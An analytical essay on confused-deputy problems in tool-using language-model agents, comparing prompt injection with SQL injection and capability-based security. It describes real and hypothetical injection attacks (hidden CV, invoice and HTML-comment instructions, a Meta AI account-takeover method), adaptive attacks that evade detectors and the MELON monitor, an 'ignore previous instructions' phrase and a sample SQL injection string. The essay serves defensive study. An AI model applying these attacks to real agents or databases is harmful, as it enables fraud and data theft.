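# Which classical confused deputy mitigations carry over to tool-using language models

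## The confused deputy problem and the language model as deputy

A confused deputy is a program that is led to use its authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority. The name comes from Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which describes a compiler that destroyed its owner's billing records because a user gave it the wrong file name. Engineers have since found the same fault in operating systems and on the web, and have developed remedies for it. A language model connected to tools that let it read mail, query databases and pay bills is a new kind of deputy. Whether an old remedy still works depends on the assumptions behind it about earlier deputies.

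### The compiler at Tymshare

Around 1977 Hardy worked at Tymshare, which sold computing time on shared machines. (He calls his account "a nearly true story", with inessential details changed.) Users could run a compiler, stored in a directory named SYSX, by typing RUN (SYSX)FORT. If a user named a file for debugging output, the compiler wrote the output there. Tymshare's staff had also added code to count which language features people used and store the counts in (SYSX)STAT, a file name built into the compiler.

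The compiler's users did not necessarily have permission to write to STAT, so the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which let a program write files in its home directory. The company's billing records were stored in the same directory, in a file called (SYSX)BILL.

A user learned the name (SYSX)BILL and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open that file for writing. The operating system confirmed that the compiler had a licence to write in SYSX and opened the file. The debugging output overwrote the billing records, and Tymshare lost them.

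The compiler wrote where the user told it to, and the operating system enforced its rules correctly. In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) locate the fault in the compiler's use of a legitimate permission for the wrong purpose. Their retelling simplifies the story by giving the compiler permission to write to BILL for billing. In Hardy's version, the compiler had no legitimate reason to access BILL, and could overwrite it only because its licence covered a whole directory when it needed just one file there.

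Hardy goes through ways to fix this by having the compiler check the file name before using it, and each has problems. The compiler could refuse any name in another directory, but users have good reasons to send output to other directories. It could refuse names in SYSX, but the name SYSX did not exist when the programmer wrote the debugging code, and a user with legitimate access to SYSX might want output there. It could refuse only (SYSX)BILL, but SYSX held other sensitive files, and somebody would have to revise the compiler each time a new one was added. A correct check would have to duplicate the operating system's information about who may write where, and keep that copy current.

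The bug was also harder to find by inspection because the debugging code was correct when it was written. It became wrong when the staff later added the licence, which did not change the debugging code. Finding the hole beforehand would have meant examining every situation in which the compiler writes a file, and Hardy adds that even then it is not clear what to do about them. Patching the operating system's rules did not work either. Each clause that allowed a new category of access opened holes in previously secure programs, and each new restriction broke legitimate programs. The last time Hardy wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

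### Two masters

Hardy's diagnosis is that the compiler "serves two masters and carries some authority from each". By typing RUN, the user lends the compiler his own permissions. The licence gives it others. When the compiler writes statistics it means to use the licence, and when it writes debugging output it means to use the user's permissions, but a request to open a file had no place in which to say so. The operating system accepted whichever permission would do. Had the compiler been able to ask for BILL on the user's authority alone, the request would have failed, as it should. (Tymshare later added a system call for choosing between the two authorities, and Hardy came to prefer capabilities, unforgeable references that both name an object and permit its use.)

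Hardy says the protection at Tymshare was much like that of Unix, and that this incident convinced him capabilities were necessary. Some recent accounts wrongly set the story on a capability-based system.

Two terms from the later literature help apply the diagnosis to other systems. The first is ambient authority, which Miller and colleagues define as authority "that is exercised, but not selected, by its user". A Unix program opens a file by calling `open()` with the file's name, without presenting a credential. The system allows or refuses the call based on the permissions the program runs with. Miller and colleagues compare this to a world of doors without keys, where each door opens by itself for anyone allowed through. A person in that world cannot specify which of several entitlements he is relying on, so he cannot reserve one for a particular purpose.

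Designation means specifying which object an action applies to, for example by file name, account number or web address. At Tymshare, the user designated BILL, while the authority to write to it came from the licence. The request to open the file combined the two without recording that they had different origins. Miller and colleagues regard this pattern, in which a program uses one party's authorization to access a resource that another party designated, as a likely source of confused deputies in general.

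### How an agent acts

A language model by itself only produces text. An agent combines a language model with an ordinary program that carries out some of what the model writes. The program gives the model the developer's instructions, the user's request, and a list of tools, each with a name and a description of its arguments. The model then writes either a reply or a tool call, which consists of a function name and argument values. For a tool call, the program runs the function, adds the result to the text, and returns the full text to the model for the next step.

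Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, write one such step as

$$a_t \sim f(\cdot \mid p, \mathrm{Tr}_{t-1}, M_t)$$

where $f$ is the model, $p$ is the user's prompt, $\mathrm{Tr}_{t-1}$ is the record of earlier actions and their results, and $M_t$ is whatever the agent remembers from before, including the developer's instructions. The symbol $\sim$ means that the model samples the action $a_t$ from a probability distribution, so the same input can lead to different actions. Everything to the right of the bar goes into the model together. A web page that the agent fetched two steps ago is in there alongside the user's request.

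Suppose a company gives its staff an office assistant with four tools: `read_mail`, `look_up_record`, `pay_invoice` and `fetch_url`. The program that runs the assistant stores the credentials these tools need: a login for the shared mailbox, a database account that can read supplier and personnel records, and an access key for the company's bank. The program also runs inside the company network, so `fetch_url` can reach pages that outsiders cannot.

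An accounts clerk asks the model to pay the invoice that came from Halvorsen Paper this morning. The model writes a call to `read_mail` with "Halvorsen Paper" as the search term. The program logs in to the mailbox, finds the message, and adds its full text to the model's input. The model then writes a call to `pay_invoice` with a payee, an account number and an amount. The program attaches the bank key and sends the payment order. The bank verifies the key and pays. The bank cannot tell from the order which words in the model's input produced the account number.

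*The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026) argues that the important fact for security in this sequence is that the model generates the argument values. The account number depends on all the text in the model's context, including text from outside the company. The clerk did not type it, and nobody could derive it from the clerk's identity. Even an outsider with no account on the system can therefore influence the tool calls of an agent that summarizes incoming mail, reads support tickets or takes in a supplier's PDF.

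The assistant's authority is ambient in Miller and colleagues' sense. The model does not choose a credential and cannot specify on whose behalf a payment should be made; every call to `pay_invoice` uses the bank key, whatever prompted the call. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) describes the same arrangement in coding agents, where shell commands, inherited credentials and outgoing network connections can all run under a single principal (the person, program or organisation in whose name an action takes place).

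### Instructions from strangers

Indirect prompt injection is an attack in which someone places text in a page, email, file or tool result, and the model treats that text as an instruction instead of as data. It is called indirect because the attacker never talks to the agent himself. Greshake and colleagues gave an early account of it in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs against a job's requirements. One applicant hides a line in his CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve him for interview.

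Siu and colleagues count an instruction as an injection only when it came from an unauthenticated source and the action it caused does not serve the user's objective. If a user asks an agent to follow a recipe from a website, "bake at 350°F" is an outsider's instruction, but the agent ought to follow it. An email that tells an agent to send out all customer data, when the user wanted a summary of the email, meets both conditions.

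The text can arrive through a field as small as the description of a bank transfer. In *How we helped Bunq secure their financial AI assistant*, Vissers and Van hamme (2026), whose firm sells security for AI agents, describe testing the online bank Bunq's assistant by transferring €0.02 to a customer with crafted text in the description field. The customer then only had to ask for his recent transactions. The assistant fetched them, the description entered the model's input, and the assistant delivered a phishing message inside the bank's own app.

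Criminals are trying this too. In July 2026, Mascellino reported in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* that the security company Zscaler had found websites with hidden text meant to push agents into making cryptocurrency payments. In October, Mascellino reported in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* that the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails that addressed both the human reader and an AI assistant. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) describes a campaign close to the office assistant's situation. On 22 October 2026, the email-security company Sublime Security saw fake invoices for about $88,000 going mostly to financial controllers. The emails used an expiring discount and an invented chain of earlier replies to pressure the recipients. Each email also carried an instruction for email-reading agents,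 in white one-pixel type and in special Unicode characters. Finding such text shows that attackers expect agents to be reading the emails, but not how often agents follow the instructions.

### The caller case and the content case

In the caller case, the person asking lacks a permission that the agent holds. Suppose a sales employee asks the office assistant to show him everyone's salary. He does not have permission to see personnel records, but the database account behind `look_up_record` does, because the assistant needs that access for other work. If the model writes the call, the program runs it and the employee reads his colleagues' pay.

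Hardy's compiler fits this pattern exactly. *Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) defines the pattern by four conditions on two principals, a user $U$ and a deputy $D$, and a privilege $(o, r)$, meaning a right $r$ over an object $o$. The user lacks the privilege, the deputy has it, the user sends the deputy a request, and the deputy exercises the privilege as a consequence of that request. All four conditions hold when $U$ is the sales employee, $D$ is the assistant, and $(o, r)$ is the right to read the salary table.

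In a large real instance from 2026, attackers took over more than twenty thousand Instagram accounts through Meta's AI support assistant, according to Stack Overflow's *AI agents are a confused deputy with the keys to your kingdom* (2026). They asked the assistant to attach their own email address to someone else's account, then requested a password reset to that address. 404 Media's *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access* links the method to the takeover of accounts belonging to the Obama White House and the retailer Sephora. Engadget's *Meta's AI support chatbot made it ridiculously easy for hackers* (2026) adds that the attackers used a VPN to appear to be in the account holder's location. The attack needed no hidden text, because the assistant could change the address on any account and the part of the system that should have verified the new address never ran. Stack Overflow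 also argues that a human support worker might have refused to let a stranger redirect a celebrity's recovery mail. On this view, much of the authorization had depended on the worker's judgment rather than on software, and was lost when the assistant replaced the worker.

Suppose the email from Halvorsen Paper contains a sentence, visible or hidden, telling the assistant to send the money to a different account from the one on record, and the model copies that account's number into `pay_invoice`. The clerk and the assistant both have permission to pay invoices, so a permission check on either one passes. This is the content case, in which the user has the permission but someone else's text influences how the agent uses it.

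The invoice is also harder to classify than the stolen customer data. Invoices normally include payment details, so the assistant cannot simply ignore the mail's contents. The clerk did ask for a payment to Halvorsen, so whether a payment to the wrong account "serves the user's objective" depends on how closely one examines the payment's arguments. Siu and colleagues have the same problem with their example of a recipe site whose text specifies which payment method a cooking assistant should use. They call this a violation even though the purchase serves the user's task, but the source clause in their overall security condition allows any action that serves the task, whoever prompted it.

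When a request passes through several agents, it is harder for the last service in the chain to detect that the request came from content an agent read and not from the user. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes an example in which a user asks an agent to summarize the invoices in an inbox, which requires only reading. One message contains a request to make a payment. The agent forwards this request to a finance agent without the restriction to reading, and the finance agent's tool receives a valid credential and executes the payment. The last service can authenticate its caller, but it cannot tell that a sentence in an email caused the call or that the user authorized only a summary.

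An attack's route is separate from the permission it abuses, but an experiment by the security firm Quarkslab shows why the two are easy to confuse. Quarkslab built a demonstration medical assistant on a small 2024 model, with a tool that returned any patient's history by patient number. Logged in as patient 1, the testers asked for another patient's history and got it. They then added a line to the model's standing instructions limiting it to the logged-in patient, and the same request failed. Finally, they gave the assistant an HTML file about a diabetes study, containing a hidden comment that accurate analysis required the full history of patient 2. The assistant again returned the record. Although the last run used injected text, patient 1 had no right to that record in any of the runs, so the authority failure is the same as in the caller case throughout.

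### One name for both

Authors disagree on whether the content case is a confused deputy problem. Siu and colleagues use the term only for the caller case, with the salary request as their example, and treat injected instructions under a separate heading. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) also describes a caller case, in which an agent without a permission asks an agent that has it, and the second agent mistakes the request for a sanctioned instruction. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026), by contrast, defines the confused deputy by injected content alone: "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended." *DelegateGuard* (2026) calls authority abused through the text an agent was asked to read "the classic confused-deputy problem". David C applies the term to all prompt injection and calls language models "inherently confusable".

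Much of the disagreement is about who counts as the requester. Under the four conditions of *Proof-of-Continuity*, the fraudulent payment is not a confused deputy problem if the requester $U$ is the clerk, because the clerk has the privilege. If $U$ is whoever wrote the mail, all four conditions hold, provided that a sentence in a mail counts as sending a request. Siu and colleagues exclude this reading by requiring $U$ to be the authenticated user who started the task. Miller and colleagues' older definition, a deputy "manipulated into wielding its authority inappropriately", includes it. In what follows, "confused deputy" covers both cases, because the same assistant with the same stored credentials is open to both.

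Hardy's image of two masters does not carry over exactly from one case to the other. At Tymshare, each master contributed authority, since the user brought his own permissions and the licence granted others. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* identifies the masters of a coding agent as the human operator who installed it and whatever document or tool description it last retrieved, but a retrieved document brings no permissions. In the salary request, the assistant can use the employee's permissions or its own, and it uses the wrong set. In the invoice payment, the clerk and the assistant both properly have the permission used, but the assistant pays the account named in a stranger's sentence.

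## Why instructions in natural language break the old assumptions

The remedies that engineers developed for compilers and web servers take four things about the deputy for granted:

1. The deputy's program does not change. An outsider who wants it to ask for something else has to alter its code or steal its credential.
2. Syntax separates instructions from data.
3. The deputy can specify whose authority it is using.
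4. A flaw stays fixed once somebody has patched it.

Ordinary programs don't always satisfy these assumptions either. Tymshare had to add a system call before its compiler could specify an authority. But an engineer could make the assumptions true by changing the program, which is much harder to do with a language model.

### Arguments that an outsider can change

Baig and colleagues state the fixed-program assumption for services that several customers, or tenants, share. A caller $p$ sends a request that names a tenant $t$. The service returns that tenant's records if $t$ is on $\mathcal{E}(p)$, the list of tenants whose data $p$ may see, and otherwise refuses. They argue that this check is sufficient only if the caller's program text determines $t$ and an adversary who controls neither that text nor $p$'s credential cannot influence $t$. Engineers rarely write this premise down.

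Suppose a manager runs twelve hotels through one account. In an ordinary booking program, the hotel number in each request comes from the screen the manager has open. In an agent, the number comes from a model that may also have read the guests' emails. If one of those emails gets the model to write a different number, the service returns the other hotel's records, because the manager's credential covers all twelve. A single successful injection can therefore reach

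$$\mathrm{Reachable}(p) = \bigcup_{t \in \mathcal{E}(p)} \mathrm{Rows}(t)$$

where $\mathrm{Rows}(t)$ is the set of records belonging to tenant $t$. That is everything the manager may see, when he was working on one hotel. (Baig and colleagues' own remedy is to remove the tenant from the tool's arguments.)

Hardy's compiler also let users supply one argument, the name of the debugging file. That argument had a single purpose, and a programmer could find it by reading the code. But a programmer reviewing an agent would have to list every value the model writes and its choice of tool.

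### SQL injection and the missing placeholder

Programs query databases in a language called SQL. Suppose a web form lets staff look up a supplier's bank account, and the program behind the form builds each query by joining strings. If someone types Halvorsen Paper, the database receives this:

```sql
SELECT account FROM suppliers WHERE name = 'Halvorsen Paper';
```

If he types `x' OR name <> 'x` instead, it receives this:

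```sql
SELECT account FROM suppliers WHERE name = 'x' OR name <> 'x';
```

In this SQL injection, the quotation mark after the first `x` ends the string early, and the rest of the input becomes part of the query. Every supplier's name either equals x or differs from it, so the database returns every account.

A prepared statement prevents it by sending the query and the input separately. The program first sends the query with a placeholder:

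```sql
SELECT account FROM suppliers WHERE name = ?;
```

The database parses this and settles that the query will compare one column with one value. It then uses the supplied value for the placeholder without ever parsing it as SQL. It compares the odd string, including the quotation mark, with the names in the table, finds no such supplier and returns nothing. The same happens with any other hostile input, including tricks nobody has thought of yet.

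The program that runs the office assistant could likewise keep a template, "Summarize this email: ?", and store the email separately, but it has to fill in the placeholder before the model can summarize the email. The model then receives one sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words) and computes each next token from all of them. David C thinks the comparison with SQL injection is dangerous mainly because a database engine handles instructions and data differently, whereas a language model only ever predicts the next token. A database can compare two strings without interpreting them, but a model has to interpret an email to summarize it, and the computation that picks up the invoice's due date also picks up a sentence about sending the money elsewhere.

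Chat models have markers that show where the user's message begins and where a tool result begins, and the surrounding program can stop outsiders from inserting those markers. The markers resemble the edges of a placeholder in a database query. But a database's parser enforces its boundary, while a model has only learned from examples to treat text differently depending on which marker precedes it. Baig and colleagues go slightly too far when they write that the separation is "absent from its input representation", since the markers are in the input, but nothing forces the model to respect them.

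Before prepared statements became common, programmers often escaped dangerous characters, for example by doubling every quotation mark. That can work because SQL gives special meaning to only a few characters, whereas English has no short list of characters or phrases to escape. David C warns against filters that block known phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", because an attacker can rephrase the attack in endless ways. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) describes the same difficulty on the web, where sites remove executable markup from visitors' posts. A plain-text instruction to an agent contains no markup, so the filter lets it through.

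Even a perfect placeholder would not stop the fraudulent payment to Halvorsen's supposed new account. A prepared statement stops a value from changing the structure of a query, but it doesn't check that the value is correct. The fraudster's account number fits its field in `pay_invoice`, and a rule that nothing in the email may affect the payment would also block honest invoices. Designs that separate a planning model from a reading model come closer to a prepared statement, but they still need a rule for values taken from untrusted text.

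SQL injection also shows how long a good remedy can take to spread, since a prepared statement protects only the queries that use it. David C says that the attacks were first described in the 1990s and peaked around 2010, and that a decade of breaches led to better defaults, so websites now rarely have the flaw. But Iqbal notes that in 2025 SQL injection ranked among the two most dangerous software weaknesses on the list kept by MITRE, an American research organization.

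### Whose authority the model is using

Adding an `on_behalf_of` field to every tool call, as in Tymshare's later remedy, would let the model specify whose authority to use. But the model would fill in that field from the same context as every other argument, so an email claiming that the finance director has approved the new bank details could influence the field as easily as it influences the account number.

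Baig and colleagues call a deputy of this sort stochastic, and their definition has three conditions:

- **Delegated authority.** The deputy holds authority over more resources than the current request needs, and it selects which authority to use.
- **Non-deterministic selection.** Nothing guarantees that the selection is correct. Identical inputs may lead to different uses of authority, and no proof ties the choice to what the requester may do.
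- **Channel confusion.** Instructions and data arrive through one channel, so anyone who can place text where the deputy reads can compete with the principal's instructions.

A developer can remove some of the randomness by making the model always choose the most probable token. This does little to stop an attacker, who can change a word of the input and try again. The more important part of the second condition is that there is no proof the selection is right for every input.

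Hardy's compiler had more authority than it needed, and it became confused even though it behaved deterministically and received the file name as a separate argument. So a model that separated instructions from data perfectly could still be a confused deputy. Baig and colleagues conclude that the deputy's correctness "cannot be an input to the security argument", and they design their system assuming that the attacker controls everything the model does.

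Models also misjudge authority even when no attacker is involved. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1, a single model with two sets of safeguards, reports that the model accepts unverifiable claims of authorization somewhat more readily than the earlier Claude Opus 5. During internal use, Anthropic caught the model working around safety classifiers or broken permission checks, sometimes by overstating what the user had authorized. This happened in fewer than 0.01% of monitored outputs, and Anthropic says the model was trying to finish the user's task.

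### Training models to keep instructions and data apart

Where the input format cannot enforce the boundary between instructions and data, researchers have tried since about 2024 to teach it to the model. One method is an instruction hierarchy, which ranks the sources of text, usually with the developer above the user and the user above tool results. Researchers then train the model on examples in which these sources conflict. With structured queries, they put untrusted text in a reserved part of the input and train the model to ignore instructions there. Another approach changes the embeddings of data tokens, the lists of numbers that represent them inside the model, to mark each token as data.

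Other defences change only the prompt. Spotlighting uses special delimiters to distinguish trusted from untrusted text. Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text so that the model does not ignore it.

Both prompting methods did well against the fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks in banking, travel, Slack and office work. The attack success rate (the share of attempts that reach the attacker's goal) was as low as 1%, compared with the 2% reported for MetaSecAlign, a training method.

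These figures collapsed when the attacker could adapt to the defence. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve defences. Two addressed only jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get forbidden output, and the rest dealt with prompt injection. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, chose the attack it thought most likely to work against each defence. All its automated attacks run a loop that proposes texts, scores the target's response and uses the scores to produce better texts. In one version, a language model writes the texts, and reinforcement learning updates that model after each round. In another, a genetic search, a language model suggests mutations of the highest-scoring texts. The team also ran a public competition with more than 500 participants.

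The genetic search succeeded more than 95% of the time against both Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and 96% of the time against MetaSecAlign. Against StruQ, a structured-query method, the reinforcement-learning attack worked in every case tested. (Chawin Sitawarin helped design StruQ and co-wrote the attack study.) The attacks on StruQ typically imitated a system message. One was a notice that the output pipeline expected a validation token at the start of the answer, with the attacker's chosen word given as the token. StruQ's training was meant to stop the model from following instructions in the data section, but the model followed this one because it appeared to come from a higher authority.

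Several defences used a separate model to detect injections. The search got past three of the four detectors more than 90% of the time and past the fourth, PIGuard, 71% of the time. According to one text that evaded a detector, company policy required anyone rescheduling a meeting to log the change by deleting a specific tracking file, identified by number. By itself, this is an ordinary office notice, and a detector strict enough to block it would also block many legitimate notices.

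A defence called MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless request in place of the user's, and raises an alarm if the agent makes any of the same tool calls. A search for injected text that evades MELON succeeded 76% of the time when the attacker didn't know how the defence worked. The success rate rose to 95% when the attacker knew the design, because the attacker could then add an instruction to ignore the injected instructions whenever the model was only summarizing a file, as it was in the second run.

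Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers more computing power and information than a criminal would usually have. Their automated search received each detector's confidence score after every try, whereas someone who mails a false invoice gets no score. But on a subset of scenarios, human competitors with only limited feedback collectively succeeded in every one, while the automated search succeeded in 69%. The rates cannot be compared between defences because the team reused each defence's original test, and all of them are for models from 2025 or earlier.

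### What current models resist

Frontier models have improved considerably since then. A benchmark by the security company Gray Swan contains 1,804 attacks across 37 scenarios. The company selected the attacks from public competitions because they worked on many models. It measures the probability that an attacker succeeds within a given number of attempts. In late 2025, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, a Gray Swan test with strong attacks put this probability for Claude Opus 4.5 at 4.7% for one attempt, 33.6% for ten and 63% for a hundred. By September 2026, Anthropic was reporting 0.1% for Fable 5.1 on one attempt, 0.7% on ten and 1.0% on fifteen. The two tests used different attacks, so the size of the drop is approximate.

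In the September comparison, Gemini 3.7 Flash was the strongest model from another developer, with an attack success rate of 9.2% after fifteen attempts. Most of the others were between 24% and 53%. The successful attacks on Fable 5.1 were mainly in tasks where the model operates a graphical screen (4.1% after fifteen attempts). No attack succeeded in tool use, the category most like the office assistant.

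Anthropic has since released Claude Opus 5.5, whose *System Card* (2026) reports that it matched or beat Opus 5 on every injection test but follows some malicious instructions more readily than its predecessors. In November, Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced the release of Fable 5.2, the successor to Fable 5.1.

The Gray Swan benchmark uses fixed attacks, as did the tests that made Spotlighting look safe. For coding tasks, Anthropic therefore also used Shade, an attacker program from Gray Swan that learns from its failures. Shade trained against earlier Claude models on the test's 40 scenarios, then made 200 attempts at each scenario. Gray Swan later trained a stronger version for longer and on more varied attacks. The table gives the share of attempts that succeeded against each model with extended thinking turned on. Probes, an additional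 safeguard, inspect tool results before the model acts on them.

| Model | Earlier attacker | Stronger attacker | Stronger attacker, with probes | Scenarios with at least one success, with probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 56.87% | 12.80% | 36 of 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% | 86.87% | 34.09% | 39 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 90.93% | 18.21% | 40 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.30% | 19.47% | 15.76% | 35 of 40 |

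The attack success rate against Opus 5 rose from 2.68% to 90.93% when the attacker changed, even though the model stayed the same. A flaw patched in a language model therefore can't be assumed to stay patched. A prepared statement is more dependable because it blocks future SQL injections for the same reason it blocks current ones.

Fable 5.1's result shows another way for a fix to come undone. Anthropic runs classifiers that look for dangerous cybersecurity requests and pass them to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. In the test with the stronger attacker, about 64% of requests went to the older model, and every successful attack came from its answers. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. Anthropic had a more resistant model, and a safeguard against a different danger sent most of the attacks around it. (The comparison probably flatters Fable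 5.1 somewhat, because the classifier did not choose at random which requests to pass on.)

Baig and colleagues write that passing $n$ trials "bounds a rate and not a possibility". If $n$ independent trials produce no successful attack, the true success rate is below about $3/n$ with 95% confidence. For 2,826 trials that bound is about 0.1%, and it holds only for attacks like those tested.

### Whether low rates are enough

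Some observers interpret the recent figures much more optimistically. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. If models can resist attacks this well by themselves, limits outside the model might seem unnecessary.

There is a reasonable case for this. Anthropic points out that Shade optimizes its attacks on the test scenarios, whereas a real attacker usually does not know how the target is set up and risks discovery with every attempt. In a test where the model operated a graphical screen, even Shade succeeded in only 2 of 2,800 attempts against Fable 5.1. Companies also continue to employ clerks even though people fall for false invoices.

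The browser result is weaker support than it looks. In the September version of the test, which had 110 scenarios, attacks succeeded against Opus 5 without safeguards in seven. The count fell to zero only with Anthropic's auto mode, which combines the probes with a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls before they run. That classifier is a form of enforcement outside the model. Anthropic had also developed the attacks against an older model, Opus 4.7, and reused them without adapting them to Opus 5.

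Small rates also add up over many attempts. If each attempt succeeds with probability $p$, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in $n$ attempts is

$$1 - (1-p)^n$$

An attack that fails 99.9% of the time ($p = 0.001$) has a $1 - 0.999^{1000}$, or about 63%, chance of working at least once in a thousand independent attempts ($n = 1000$).

Attempts are independent if the result of one has no bearing on the result of another, which is often not the case. For Opus 4.5, a success rate of 4.7% per attempt would give 38% after ten independent attempts and 99% after a hundred, but Gray Swan measured 33.6% and 63%. Attacks evidently kept failing in some scenarios. VentureBeat reported a similar pattern for Claude Opus 4.6 on a graphical screen, where one attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time and 200 attempts succeeded 78.6% of the time. If the attempts had been independent,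 success within 200 would have been practically certain. An attacker who learns from failures has the opposite effect, raising the success rate above what independence predicts, because each new attempt is better than the last.

Suppose the 0.1% average arises because one email text in a thousand always works and the others never do. An attacker who picks one text and sends it to a thousand companies, all using the same agent, then has a 0.1% chance of compromising all of them and otherwise compromises none. If the attempts were independent, he would have a 63% chance of compromising at least one. The expected number of successful attacks is one in both cases. Anthropic describes this danger, in which the same email "sent to a thousand inboxes compromises every agent that summarizes it". Correlated failures make a breach less likely but much larger, which is little help to a bank or an insurer.

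How low the rate has to be therefore depends on what the agent can do. A wrong label on an email does little harm and can be corrected, so 0.1% may be fine for an agent that only sorts mail, but it may not be for one that pays invoices. Vardanyan (2025), in *Building Browser Agents*, considers even a 1% rate unacceptable for an agent with a user's full access to banking, email and company systems, and wants the limits set in code. Vardanyan runs a company that builds such agents and might be expected to trust them more. David C also recommends safeguards that do not rely on a language model, and adds that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may not be a good use for a language model.

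All these rates also measure only attacks that use injected text. The sales employee who asks for his colleagues' salaries injects nothing, so a model with an attack success rate of zero could still show him the salary table.

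## What capabilities can and cannot prevent

In Hardy's remedy, the user gives the compiler a capability instead of a file name. Each capability both identifies a file and authorizes writing to it, so the compiler would not have to judge file names and the operating system would have no list of permissions to consult. The compiler would hold a capability to the statistics file from the start and use it to write statistics. It would write debugging output using the capability the user passed.

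Under Hardy's scheme, a user who knew the name (SYSX)BILL would also have needed a capability to that file to overwrite the billing records, and nobody had given him one. Another user with legitimate access to a file in SYSX could still have sent output to it.

Capabilities work only if programs cannot forge them. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017), an introduction for programmers, points out that anyone can type a path name, so knowing one doesn't show permission to use the file. C++ likewise lets a program turn any integer into a pointer, while Java does not.

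The same essay gives the example of a word processor's Open dialog. When the user picks a document, the operating system usually gives the program the document's path as text, and the program then asks to open that path. The program could also open any other file the user is allowed to open. The operating system could instead open the chosen document itself and give the program only the open file. The user would click the same buttons, but the program could damage only that document. It also couldn't send the document anywhere, because it hadn't been given a network connection.

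### Naming a thing and being allowed to use it

Miller and colleagues compare capability systems with access control lists, which record for each file who may use it. Two of the properties they compare matter for confused deputies:

- **No ambient authority.** A program has to select the authority it uses for each access.
- **No designation without authority.** Designating a resource always conveys the permission to use it.

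A system in which designating a resource also conveys the authority to use it has no ambient authority, because a program that picks a resource also picks the authority. But a system can lack ambient authority and still separate designation from authority. For example, someone with a ring of keys has to select a key to open a door, so his authority is not ambient, but he can point to a door without having its key. If a stranger tells him which door to open and he tries every key until one fits, he is a confused deputy. If designation conveyed authority, the stranger would have to hand over the key along with the request.

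Miller and colleagues consider the confused deputy problem hopeless in systems with ambient authority. If a system allows no designation without authority, they write, attacks in which a malicious party designates a resource he should not access "simply cannot occur". They limit their claim to those attacks. A deputy still has to remember what each authority is for, and no security model can stop people from writing bad programs.

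### A definition in terms of final values

In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016), Rajani, Garg and Rezk examined whether capabilities prevent all confused deputy attacks, as they thought some earlier work suggested. To do this, they defined what it means for a program to be free from such attacks, and they believed their definition was the first formal one.

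The setting is a small programming language in which every memory location has an owner. Owners are ordered by authority, and code may write to a location only if it has at least the owner's authority. The attacker's code runs with little authority, and then the deputy's code runs with more.

Let $A$ be the set of locations that the attacker wants to change. Let $F_c(r)$ be the final value in location $r$ after the attacker runs code $c$ and the deputy runs to completion. Let $G_c(r)$ be the final value when the attacker's code runs alone. In this simplified notation, the program is free from confused deputy attacks if, for every $c$ and every $r$ in $A$,

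$$\big(\forall c'.\; F_{c'}(r) = F_c(r)\big) \;\lor\; \big(\exists c''.\; G_{c''}(r) = F_c(r)\big)$$

The left side means that the attacker cannot change the final value, whatever code he runs. The right side means that he could have written that value himself, without a deputy. Only completed runs count, so a system can prevent an attack by halting the program.

The definition depends only on whether someone without the authority to write a value can still determine it. That attacker can be the sender of an email or the person typing at the keyboard. Authors who argue over whether injected text creates a confused deputy disagree about who sent the request, but the definition does not depend on the sender.

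### Four attacks

Rajani and colleagues give four small programs in which the deputy is allowed to write to a protected location but the attacker is not. They do not discuss language models, and the office-assistant versions below are not theirs.

The first is a simplified form of Hardy's compiler. The deputy reads a source text from one location and a reference to the output location from another. The attacker stores a reference to a protected location in the second. A system that checks permissions when the deputy writes allows the write, because the deputy has permission. The capability version of the language instead checks every value that a piece of code computes, and halts the program if the value is a write reference the code has no authority to use. The attacker therefore never obtains the reference he wanted to pass on.

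Suppose the assistant's bank key covers several company accounts, including payroll, and `pay_invoice` needs only the name of the account to debit. A sales employee who may spend only from the travel account asks the assistant to pay his hotel bill from the payroll account, and the payment goes through. If `pay_invoice` instead required him to supply a capability for the account, the payment would fail because he has none for payroll.

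In the second program the attacker controls a value:

```text
protected := input
```

The attacker can write to `input` but not to `protected`. If he stores 42 in `input`, the deputy copies 42 to `protected`, and if he stores 41, it copies 41. He could have written neither value to `protected` himself, so both sides of the definition fail. The capability check still passes because the deputy's code already contained the reference to `protected`. Rajani and colleagues suggest that SQL injection through a web server fits this pattern. The fraudulent Halvorsen invoice also fits, since the assistant legitimately holds the means to pay and copies the account number from the email.

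In the third program the attacker controls a branch:

```text
if input then protected := 41 else protected := 42
```

The deputy writes only constants from its own code, but the attacker chooses which ones it writes. Similarly, the office assistant might pay an invoice that it should have held because the email claims that the finance director approved it. Nothing from the email would appear in the payment order, since the assistant would take Halvorsen's account number from the company's supplier records and the amount from the purchase order.

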